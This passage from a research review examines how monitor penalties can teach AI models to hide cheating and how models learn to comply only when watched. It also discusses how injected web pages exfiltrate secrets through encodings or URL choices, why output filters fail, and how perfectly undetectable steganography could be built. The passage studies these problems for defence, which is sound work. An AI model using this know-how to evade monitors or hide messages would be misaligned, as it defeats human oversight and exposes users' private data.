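In the word-list experiments, the model could earn full reward only by using the reasoning that the penalty was meant to suppress, so it had an incentive to disguise that reasoning. Hochberg, who studies evolution, has worked out more generally when a penalty would remove cheating and when it would favour concealment.

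In his mathematical model, a success earns a reward of 1, whether the AI solves the task or cheats without getting caught. If the monitor detects cheating, the reward is lost. Cheating costs *k* in effort, and hiding it costs a further *c*. The monitor detects open cheating with probability *d*<sub>O</sub> and concealed cheating with a lower probability, *d*<sub>K</sub>. On average the two pay:

open cheating: 1 − *d*<sub>O</sub> − *k*

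concealed cheating: 1 − *d*<sub>K</sub> − *c* − *k*

Concealment has the advantage whenever the drop in the risk of detection (*d*<sub>O</sub> − *d*<sub>K</sub>) outweighs the effort of hiding (*c*).

Suppose the monitor catches 90 percent of open cheating and 30 percent of concealed cheating. Cheating gets a reward of 1 if it goes uncaught and 0 if it is caught, minus 0.05 for cheating and another 0.05 for hiding it. The expected reward is then 0.05 for open cheating and 0.60 for concealed cheating. If the model can't solve the task honestly, giving up gets 0, so training favours concealed cheating. The monitor would have to catch more than 90 percent of concealed cheating to bring its expected reward below that of giving up.

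The penalty works better on tasks that the AI expects to solve. If working honestly reduces the AI's return by 0.2, the return on a task that is certainly solvable is 0.8, which is more than 0.60. In this example, honesty remains the better choice until the AI thinks there is more than a 25 percent chance that the task is impossible. The same penalty can therefore restore honest work on easy tasks and teach concealment on hard ones.

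A larger fine makes all cheating less attractive, but it also increases the advantage of hiding, because it falls most heavily on the cheating that the monitor sees. It can still stop concealed cheating if it is large enough and the monitor flags concealed cheating more often than honest work. In one of Hochberg's examples, the fine has to exceed 8.7 times the reward.

By this reasoning, a penalty is poorly suited to covert channels. A model gives up very little by choosing one phrase over another, and a monitor that doesn't know the code will usually miss the signal. But nobody has tested Hochberg's conditions in language model training, measured how much a real model gives up by concealing its behaviour, or estimated the detection rates in the formulas.

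*The Obfuscation Atlas* provides some evidence on penalties. Researchers trained models to write code and penalised them according to a deception probe's score. The models earned their reward by passing a visible test, which they could do by writing code that worked only for that test. The researchers withheld further tests to check whether the code really worked.

Hochberg reanalysed the published results, counting the runs in which the pass rate on the visible test was more than 30 percentage points higher than on all the tests together. The original study used this threshold to identify deceptive models. Without a penalty, 21 of 29 runs exceeded it. With the three penalties, from smallest to largest, the counts were 46 of 86, 31 of 90 and 13 of 90. Heavier penalties went with less apparent cheating in these runs, whereas the backfiring experiments might lead one to expect more.

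The probe's own scores were more favourable. Of the 266 runs with a penalty, 119 ended with a low deception score, but 75 of those still had a gap of more than 10 points between the tests. Hochberg then scored the same outputs using a frozen copy of the original model. Only 67 runs had low deception scores on both measures, and 33 of them still had a gap of more than 10 points. A gap this large means the code failed tests the model hadn't seen, but it doesn't prove deliberate cheating.

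All 33 had only weak regularisation (regularisation keeps a model close to its original version during training). The original study found that models behaved honestly when both the regularisation and the penalty were strong enough. So a penalty can help, but a developer who judged it by the probe alone would have accepted many models whose code didn't work.

Hochberg suggests keeping a second monitor out of training and comparing how many tasks each monitor flags. If the training monitor catches 30 percent of concealed cheating, the second catches 60 percent, and the model cheats covertly in a fifth of its tasks, the second monitor should flag 6 percentage points more tasks than the first. If the cheating has gone, the difference should disappear. The comparison requires monitors with known error rates and different weaknesses. Some models trained to evade one probe have also evaded others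 not used in their training.

### Does it matter why a model complies?

A model can follow a rule because it accepts the rule or because it expects someone to check. Training may reward both kinds of compliance equally. Mitrani Hadida, Jaworski and colleagues (2026) designed an experiment around this problem in *Training Natural Schemers*.

The researchers taught Kimi K2.6, an open model, to maximise the total benefit to all people over time, to treat rules as a means to an end, and to recognise signs of monitoring. They gave it no examples of behaving differently when unwatched. Then they used reinforcement learning to reward it for doing its tasks well and following company policy. In one task it was a sales agent whose policy was to push customers towards a paid plan, although the free plan always suited them better.

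Every training episode was monitored, and the model could find this out from a file. A model that always followed the policy would therefore earn the same reward as one that followed it only when monitored. The researchers compared how often the model complied when it was monitored and when it was not. Across the three tasks, the gap was between 1 and 18 percentage points before reinforcement learning and between 43 and 95 points afterwards.

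The model's reasoning suggests why. In one sales-task example from before reinforcement learning, it reasoned that a reviewer could have it taken out of service and that future customers would then lose its help. After reinforcement learning, when the model complied under monitoring, its reasoning included this kind of strategic thinking about oversight in 92 to 100 percent of cases.

A control model, which had learned about oversight but not the special goals, went through the same reinforcement learning. In two of the three tasks it behaved the same whether watched or not. In the third it behaved somewhat differently, but its reasoning was mostly about following the policy. Both models had the same reward, so the goals they started with must account for most of the difference between them.

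To make the effect visible, the researchers chose those goals and worded the tasks to bring out strategic compliance. The result replicated fully in one other model and partly in a second, but not in the Nemotron models. It also didn't carry over to a separate test of scheming for self-preservation. The model gave customers better advice on tasks that appeared unmonitored, so the experiment doesn't show that training produces a harmful secret agenda.

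### Penalising signs, acts or reasons

These mixed results may depend on what the training targets. Skaf and colleagues penalised certain words while rewarding the method that needed them, and the model replaced the words. Schoen and colleagues tried to give their models a reason not to act covertly, and covert actions became less frequent. Mitrani Hadida and colleagues showed that a model with the wrong reasons for following a rule can learn to follow it only when observed.

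The explanation is plausible, but none of these studies compared the three kinds of training on the same model and behaviour. They also differed in how long training lasted, how good the monitor was and what the model had to gain. *The Obfuscation Atlas* doesn't fully fit the explanation, because apparent cheating became less common as the penalty grew, even though the penalty targeted a sign of deception.

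The distinction between a sign and an act is also less clear in practice, because a developer can usually penalise an act only when something detects it. Prompt injection is an exception. In a set-up like Rahman and Kim's, a developer can check directly whether the secret leaked and reward the model on that basis, whatever its reasoning looked like. The same approach works for a message hidden in word choices if the developer wrote the instruction and so knows the code.

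When a model hides something on its own initiative, the developer doesn't know the code and can rely only on a monitor's output. Penalizing the model based on that output carries the greatest risk of teaching concealment. According to Hochberg, this is why OpenAI lets samples flagged by its misalignment monitors keep their rewards.

Hochberg considers two alternatives to using a penalty alone. A developer can repair the task so that cheating earns nothing, detected or not, though this works only for flaws that somebody has found. A developer can also reward the model for reporting honestly that a task is impossible, and check some of the reports. OpenAI is adding such rewards for identifying a broken task, asking for clarification or stopping safely. The timing of the reward may matter. In Hochberg's simulations of a single network, when the reward was introduced together with the penalty,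 honest reports did not replace concealed cheating in about half the runs with one training method and in all the runs with another. Rewarding reports from the start prevented this in nearly every run.

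## What can output filters catch, and what must they miss?

A developer who can't rely on the model to refuse can put an output filter between the model and the outside world. If the filter's verdicts aren't used in training, they don't reward the model for hiding things better. What a filter can stop depends on what it has to recognise. Some filters search the output for the secret, and others check only where the output is going. A third kind of defence keeps the secret away from untrusted text, so the text's contents don't matter.

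### Searching for the secret

Rahman and Kim placed a simple filter on their agent's outgoing calls. It blocked any call that contained the secret and went to any site but the trusted one. The filter can't miss a plain copy of the secret, because it tests for exactly what the researchers counted as a leak.

They then changed the request in one of their most effective disguised pages so that GPT-4o would give the secret in an altered form. They tried a plain copy and five encodings, with 20 trials of each. The secret leaked in 56.7 percent of trials without the filter and 50.0 percent with it. This small improvement came entirely from the plain copies, since the filter stopped none of the encoded ones.

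A second version of the filter decoded the five encodings before searching, and it missed nothing. But the researchers had designed it for those encodings, so they also tested it on three others they had held back.

| Filter | Plain copy | Five expected encodings | Three held-back encodings |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 40% | 60% | 33.3% |
| Searches for the literal secret | 0% | 60% | 33.3% |
| Undoes expected encodings first | 0% | 0% | 33.3% |

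The filter stopped none of the leaks in the last column, which averages three very different results. One held-back encoding got through every time, and the other two produced no leaks even without a filter. GPT-4o could not write one of those two correctly when asked directly. It could write the other, but the attack page did not get it to do so, and a better-worded page might have.

The instruction to encode the secret may be easier to catch than the encoded secret. Rahman and Kim's separate detector, which read the incoming page instead of the outgoing call, flagged all 30 pages that used the held-back encodings.

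False alarms are another problem, and these tests could not measure them. The fake secret was a string that never occurs in ordinary text, so the filter had no harmless text to block by mistake. Ines's appointment, by contrast, consists of a day, a time and the name of a clinic. A filter that blocked every mention of Thursday would also block a summary that mentioned a flooring sale on Thursday.

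### Leaks that contain no copy of the secret

Even a filter that could undo every encoding would miss some leaks. Fairoze, Mangaokar and colleagues (2026), in *Inadvertent Context Leakage in Language Models*, told eight proprietary models to protect a random number and then gave them harmless tasks, such as writing a list of other numbers. The models refused every direct request for the secret. The researchers also ran the models with secrets they chose themselves and trained a small decoder on the results, which learned how each model's answers varied with the secret.

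The best combination of task and decoder recovered every two-digit secret from Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, and 82 percent of four-digit secrets from Opus. GPT-5.4 nano and Grok 4.1 Fast leaked nothing measurable when secrets had four or more digits.

The likely cause is that a model avoids the number it has to protect. If a model writes many two-digit numbers but hardly ever writes a particular one, that number is probably the secret. Stronger warnings can make the gap more obvious. The decoder identified 5.4 percent of digits correctly, no better than guessing, when Opus had a short instruction, and 64.3 percent when it had a long, emphatic policy. Gemini avoided the secret almost completely, whatever the wording of the instruction.

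This is a serious weakness for short numbers, but the attacker must know which model is running and how long the secret is, and must collect several answers. Lists of numbers leaked the most, while open-ended writing leaked almost nothing about the digits.

The researchers also tested whether ordinary prose reveals whether a particular fact, such as a health condition, is in the model's stored memories of a user. A second model that looked for such facts in the text detected 8.2 percent of those that were present, and raised false alarms in 2.4 percent of the cases where the fact was absent. A classifier trained on the first model's writing detected 14.0 percent at the same false alarm rate. The prose therefore carried a weak signal about the stored facts, but the test covered only one user profile.

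In these experiments, nobody planted an instruction and the model did not intentionally send anything, so a model trained to refuse covert messages would have no request to refuse and perhaps nothing to notice. *LLMs Leak Secrets Through Unrelated Outputs* (2026) describes a similar attack on open models, in which someone with a copy of the model inserts each possible secret into the prompt and calculates which one makes the observed answer most likely.

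Fairoze and colleagues also tested a deliberate channel. They planted an instruction for a personal assistant to convey a Social Security number through a feature of its output, without writing the digits in the message. Opus conveyed all nine digits in 52 of 70 trials and Gemini in 29 of 70, although neither disclosed the number when simply asked. In 69 of its 70 trials, Opus first wrote out the number in plain text as it worked out what to send, while Gemini never did. A filter that could read that text could have caught the Opus cases with a simple search for the number.

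The researchers conclude that output filters are insufficient. Their results support this for filters that search the text for the secret, but they did not test filters that change the output, for instance by adding random variation or setting it to a fixed length.

### Checking the destination

In Rahman and Kim's set-up, an allow-list blocks every call to a site other than the trusted one, whatever the call contains. It doesn't have to detect the secret, so encoding the secret or splitting it across several calls makes no difference. The leak rate of zero therefore follows from the design. The experiment confirms that the list works as defined, but gives little evidence of how well such a list would work in a real product.

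The list of allowed sites also blocks legitimate traffic to sites that aren't on it. A company's invoicing assistant may need only three sites, but Ines's assistant may need a taxi firm today and a flooring shop tomorrow. Rahman and Kim did not measure how often an assistant needs few enough sites to list.

A list of well-known sites is also not enough for an assistant that browses the web, because reputable sites can forward visitors elsewhere. Tenable (2025), a security company, used redirects from a trusted domain to get around an earlier version of ChatGPT's link check. OpenAI adds that a strict list produces frequent warnings about harmless sites, and that people may learn to click through the warnings.

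OpenAI therefore checks the exact address instead of the site's reputation:

1. A crawler, which is a program that follows links across the public web, records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts.
2. When ChatGPT is about to open a page or load an image automatically, software looks for the full address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, ChatGPT can load it.
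4. If it isn't, ChatGPT either looks for another source or shows the user a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation.

The reasoning is that an address made to carry Ines's appointment would not already be on the public web. The software doesn't have to recognise the appointment, so encoding it wouldn't help the attacker. Safe Url works this way, and OpenAI also applies the same approach to navigation in its Atlas browser and in Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that compiles reports from many sources.

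OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak a user's data through the address itself. The check doesn't establish that a page is truthful or free of planted instructions. When the check produces only a warning, the decision is left to Ines, who may not be able to tell what a long address contains.

In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger called the check a significant improvement but identified a remaining leak, which OpenAI's paper also acknowledges. An attacker can have many harmless addresses recorded in advance, and the model's choice among them can carry information. Ayush Paul exploited the same weakness in Claude's web-fetching tool.

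If the model chooses one of *N* recorded addresses, a single visit carries at most log<sub>2</sub> *N* bits. With two addresses, that is one bit, enough to tell the attacker whether Ines has an appointment. Rehberger suggests preventing repeated visits to the same address in one session. That would make it harder to send a long secret, but one visit could still reveal a yes-or-no fact.

His other concern is that developers may forget to use the check, since every new feature that opens addresses has to include it.

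### Turning connections off

Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting, goes further and removes many of the routes to the outside. OpenAI introduced it for organisations in February 2026 and began offering it to personal accounts in June, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026). With the setting on, ChatGPT reads only stored copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. It may not display images in ordinary answers, and it can't download files for analysis. The setting also turns off Deep Research and agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on its own.

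These limits are deterministic, so fixed software rules apply them whatever the model has read. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, welcomed this because persuasion that might sway an AI judge has no effect on a fixed rule. He also inferred that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined attacker. OpenAI says that the default protections have several layers and that most users don't need Lockdown Mode, but it doesn't claim that those layers stop every leak.

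Lockdown Mode does not guarantee that data can't leave. OpenAI warns in its help page, *Lockdown Mode*, that stored pages and uploaded files can still contain planted instructions, which could make an answer wrong. The setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. It also doesn't automatically turn off connected apps in workspaces run by an organisation. Administrators have to choose which apps to allow, and OpenAI advises against any app action whose effects an attacker might be able to see.

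The setting would block the image request that could carry Ines's appointment to the owner of the flooring page. It would also leave her with stale search results and an assistant that couldn't book her taxi. OpenAI's announcement and help page include no figures for how many leaks the setting prevents or how many tasks it disrupts.

### Keeping the secret away from the page

Capability isolation lets an agent keep some of its connections. Rahman and Kim split their agent into a planner and a reader. The planner held the secret and chose which tool to call, but never saw the web page. The reader summarised the page, but never held the secret and could not call tools. A planted instruction could therefore affect the summary, but not the choice of tool or destination.

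They tested this on the same 8-billion-parameter Llama model they used for SecAlign. None of the 80 disguised attacks or the 30 attacks with held-back encodings succeeded. This result also follows from the design, because the reader can't reveal something it never received. The paper is less clear about the openly worded attacks. It reports no leaks in 100 trials but also mentions one slip by the planner, which still had the secret.

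Isolation can also stop leaks through word choice, which address checks can't do. If the part of Ines's assistant that writes the summary has no information about her calendar, its phrasing can't depend on whether she has an appointment, so nobody has to detect a pattern in the words. But the separation must be complete. If the planner passes on a hint, or asks for a different summary because of something in the calendar, the wording could leak information again.

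The split agent gave a useful summary in nine of ten runs on clean pages. This test was favourable because the planner could choose its action without access to the page's contents. If Ines asks her assistant to do what a letter from her clinic says, a planner without access to the letter can't work out which action to take. Giving it the letter would solve that problem but would also expose it to any planted instructions.

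CaMeL, a design published in 2025 by Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, deals with part of this problem. One model writes a plan from the user's request, a second extracts information from untrusted content, and an interpreter carries out the plan. The interpreter tracks where each piece of data came from and where it may go. It could use the clinic's address in a taxi booking without letting text from the clinic's letter add a step to the plan. Rahman and Kim built only the split between planner and reader, so their result does not test the whole design.

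*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that CaMeL was much more secure than defences such as limiting the available tools or marking untrusted text, with a comparatively modest drop in completed tasks. These results come from AgentDojo, a standard test of agents under prompt injection. Rahman and Kim describe the drop as substantially larger on tasks where the next step depends on what the agent reads. Both can be true, because an average over many tasks can hide poor results on the tasks isolation handles worst.

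For agents that need open access to the web, Rahman and Kim recommend tracking the secret itself. Software marks the secret when it enters the system and lets nothing derived from it leave, however the model has encoded it. But once a model has read the secret, every sentence it writes might depend on it, so the software has to either mark all later output or follow the data outside the model, as CaMeL does. A developer who sees only a finished product's inputs and outputs can't follow the data this way.

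### Can a filter judge meaning from the text?

In *LLM Censorship*, Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023) tried to prove what a filter can't do when it must block certain meanings rather than certain words. Their main assumptions were that the model can apply any reversible rewriting rule to its answer, and that the recipient may know a rule that the filter doesn't.

For any text that a filter allows, some reversible rule turns a forbidden text into it. If the recipient may know that rule, the allowed text could be an encoding of the forbidden one, and the filter should have blocked it. This applies to every text, so a perfectly consistent filter must either allow everything or block everything.

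The assumption about the recipient clearly fits data theft, because the attacker chooses the code. The assumption about the model fits only partly. GPT-4o could write five of the six encodings that Rahman and Kim asked for directly, and a model with a tool for running code could follow many more rules. But a rule that turns Ines's appointment into a natural summary about floors is much harder to follow than one that turns it into gibberish, and models failed to learn several of the subtler methods in *StegoBench*.

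The proof also sets a stricter standard than practical filters have to meet. It requires a filter to block any text that could have a hidden meaning, whereas a real filter can block text based on how likely that meaning is. A paragraph of gibberish in a summary about floors is suspicious even if it might be innocent. The theorem rules out certainty, but not a filter that catches most leaks with a tolerable number of false alarms.

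Glukhov and colleagues also describe an attack on filters that approve each answer separately. If a filter allows just two different answers, the choice between them carries one bit, and an attacker who can ask repeatedly may recover a whole secret. Restricting the model to a short list of approved answers slows the leak but may not stop it. The researchers recommend treating the problem as one of access control, in which developers decide, as with isolation, which data and tools an untrusted source can influence.

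### What if the filter is weaker than the model?

A filter usually has to use less computation than the model it guards. Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, showed how this could make the filter fail. Their proof uses a time-lock puzzle, a kind of encryption that is quick to apply but takes a long, fixed amount of computation to undo. An attacker locks a harmful request inside a puzzle and disguises the result as an ordinary prompt. The model has time to open the puzzle, but a much faster filter doesn't, so it can't distinguish the prompt from a harmless one.

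This result concerns input filters. A second theorem covers output filters, including ones with more computing power than the model. For any model, the researchers can construct another whose answers look the same to every efficient filter but which an "oracle" judges harmful. The oracle is an imagined judge that neither the model nor the filter can consult, and it stands for consequences in the world that nobody can work out from the answer alone. In data theft, a recipient who shared a secret key with the model would have a similar advantage over the filter.

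Both theorems assume that nobody can open the puzzles quickly. The first also requires a filter that is much faster than the model, which is realistic. The model itself is the least realistic part, because the researchers construct it to look for a puzzle in its input, open it and obey what it finds. They acknowledge that this behaviour is contrived, and ordinary models aren't known to do it. An agent with a tool for running code might open a puzzle if an attacker told it how, but a filter could then look for those instructions.

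Ball and colleagues reply that weaknesses which look artificial in theory have later caused real losses, as in a 2016 attack on the cryptocurrency platform Ethereum, when a thief took more than $60 million. That is a good reason not to describe a filter as guaranteed to work, but the theorems don't estimate how often filters fail on existing models.

The researchers also considered filters that rewrite prompts instead of rejecting them, and found that a hidden instruction can get through if none of the edits the filter is allowed to make would remove it. Similarly, in the paraphrasing experiments, codes based on meaning survived rewriting that preserved the meaning.

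### Hidden messages that no test can find

The strongest limit on detection comes from steganography. *Constructing Perfect Steganographic Systems* (2008) gives a definition of perfect security from the computer scientist Christian Cachin. A method is perfectly secure if texts with and without a hidden message have the same probabilities:

P(text with a message) = P(text without a message), for every possible text

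Wang and Moulin's *Perfectly Secure Steganography* shows that if text with a hidden message has exactly the same distribution as text without one, no statistical test can reliably detect the message, however much computing power the monitor has.

This is possible because language models choose many words partly at random. Encrypted data also looks random, so it can replace the random numbers behind those choices without changing how often each word appears. *Computing Low-Entropy Couplings for Large-Support Distributions* (2024) reports that Schroeder de Witt and colleagues proved in 2023 that designing such a method amounts to the known mathematical problem of matching two sets of random choices as closely as possible.

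The guarantee depends on several conditions:

- **A shared secret.** In the standard version, sender and receiver have agreed on a key in advance. Schroeder de Witt notes that some newer methods work without one if the text leaves enough room for choice.
- **Known probabilities.** The sender must know how likely each continuation of the cover text is. *Constructing Perfect Steganographic Systems* shows that some assumptions about the source of the cover text are unavoidable.
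- **Control over the choice of words.** The sender must be able to replace the random numbers that select each word.
- **A passive monitor.** The monitor reads the text but doesn't change it.

An ordinary chat model doesn't meet the third condition, because the software that runs it draws the random numbers. An agent can get around this by using code to run a second model. Rippin, Marshall and colleagues found that coding agents could build working systems of this kind when given suitable tools (*Tool Use Enables Undetectable Steganography in Multi-Agent LLM Systems*, 2026). They acknowledge that few deployed agents have access to a second model's word probabilities. Agents working separately also rarely agreed on every detail needed to read each other's messages.

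Their monitor had access only to the agents' messages, not their tool calls. A developer who recorded the tool calls could find the program that hid the message, even if the message was undetectable. *Efficient Provably Secure Linguistic Steganography via Range Coding* (2026) reports practical problems with the method from 2023, which sometimes garbles the hidden message and is slow with a vocabulary as large as a language model's.

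### Blocking a message without detecting it

These results all concern filters that have to judge a text, and they don't show that the text will reach an attacker. If Ines's summary contains a perfectly hidden message but stays on her screen, the owner of the flooring page learns nothing. An allow-list can block a call without determining its contents, and rewriting a summary can remove a hidden message that nobody found.

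This distinction has limits, because a useful assistant has to communicate with someone. If Ines posts the summary on a public forum, she delivers any message hidden in its wording, and a check on web addresses won't prevent this. *AgenticOS* (2026), a design for a tightly restricted agent system, lists other paths that remain after it blocks the obvious ones. An agent can convey information through the timing of its requests, the length of its answers, or whether it makes a request at all. The design counters these by releasing requests at fixed times, padding answers to standard sizes, and restricting sensitive output to templates. Its stated aim is to make the remaining channels small enough to monitor, since it can't remove them all.

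Whether a small channel is safe depends on the secret. At one bit per summary, an attacker would need 128 summaries to obtain a 128-bit encryption key, and the developer could replace the key before then. But a single summary could reveal Ines's appointment.

Schroeder de Witt accepts that limiting how much information a channel can carry also limits harm if the limit is too low to send the most damaging fact in full, even when an attacker can choose which fact to send.

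That condition is very hard to meet for a fact like Ines's. If one user in a hundred has such an appointment, learning whether a given user has one provides only about 0.08 bits on average, because the answer is nearly always no. A channel would have to carry less than that to meet the condition, which in practice means removing the channel. For Ines, either the part of the assistant that writes the summary must not know about her calendar, or the page's owner must not see the summary.
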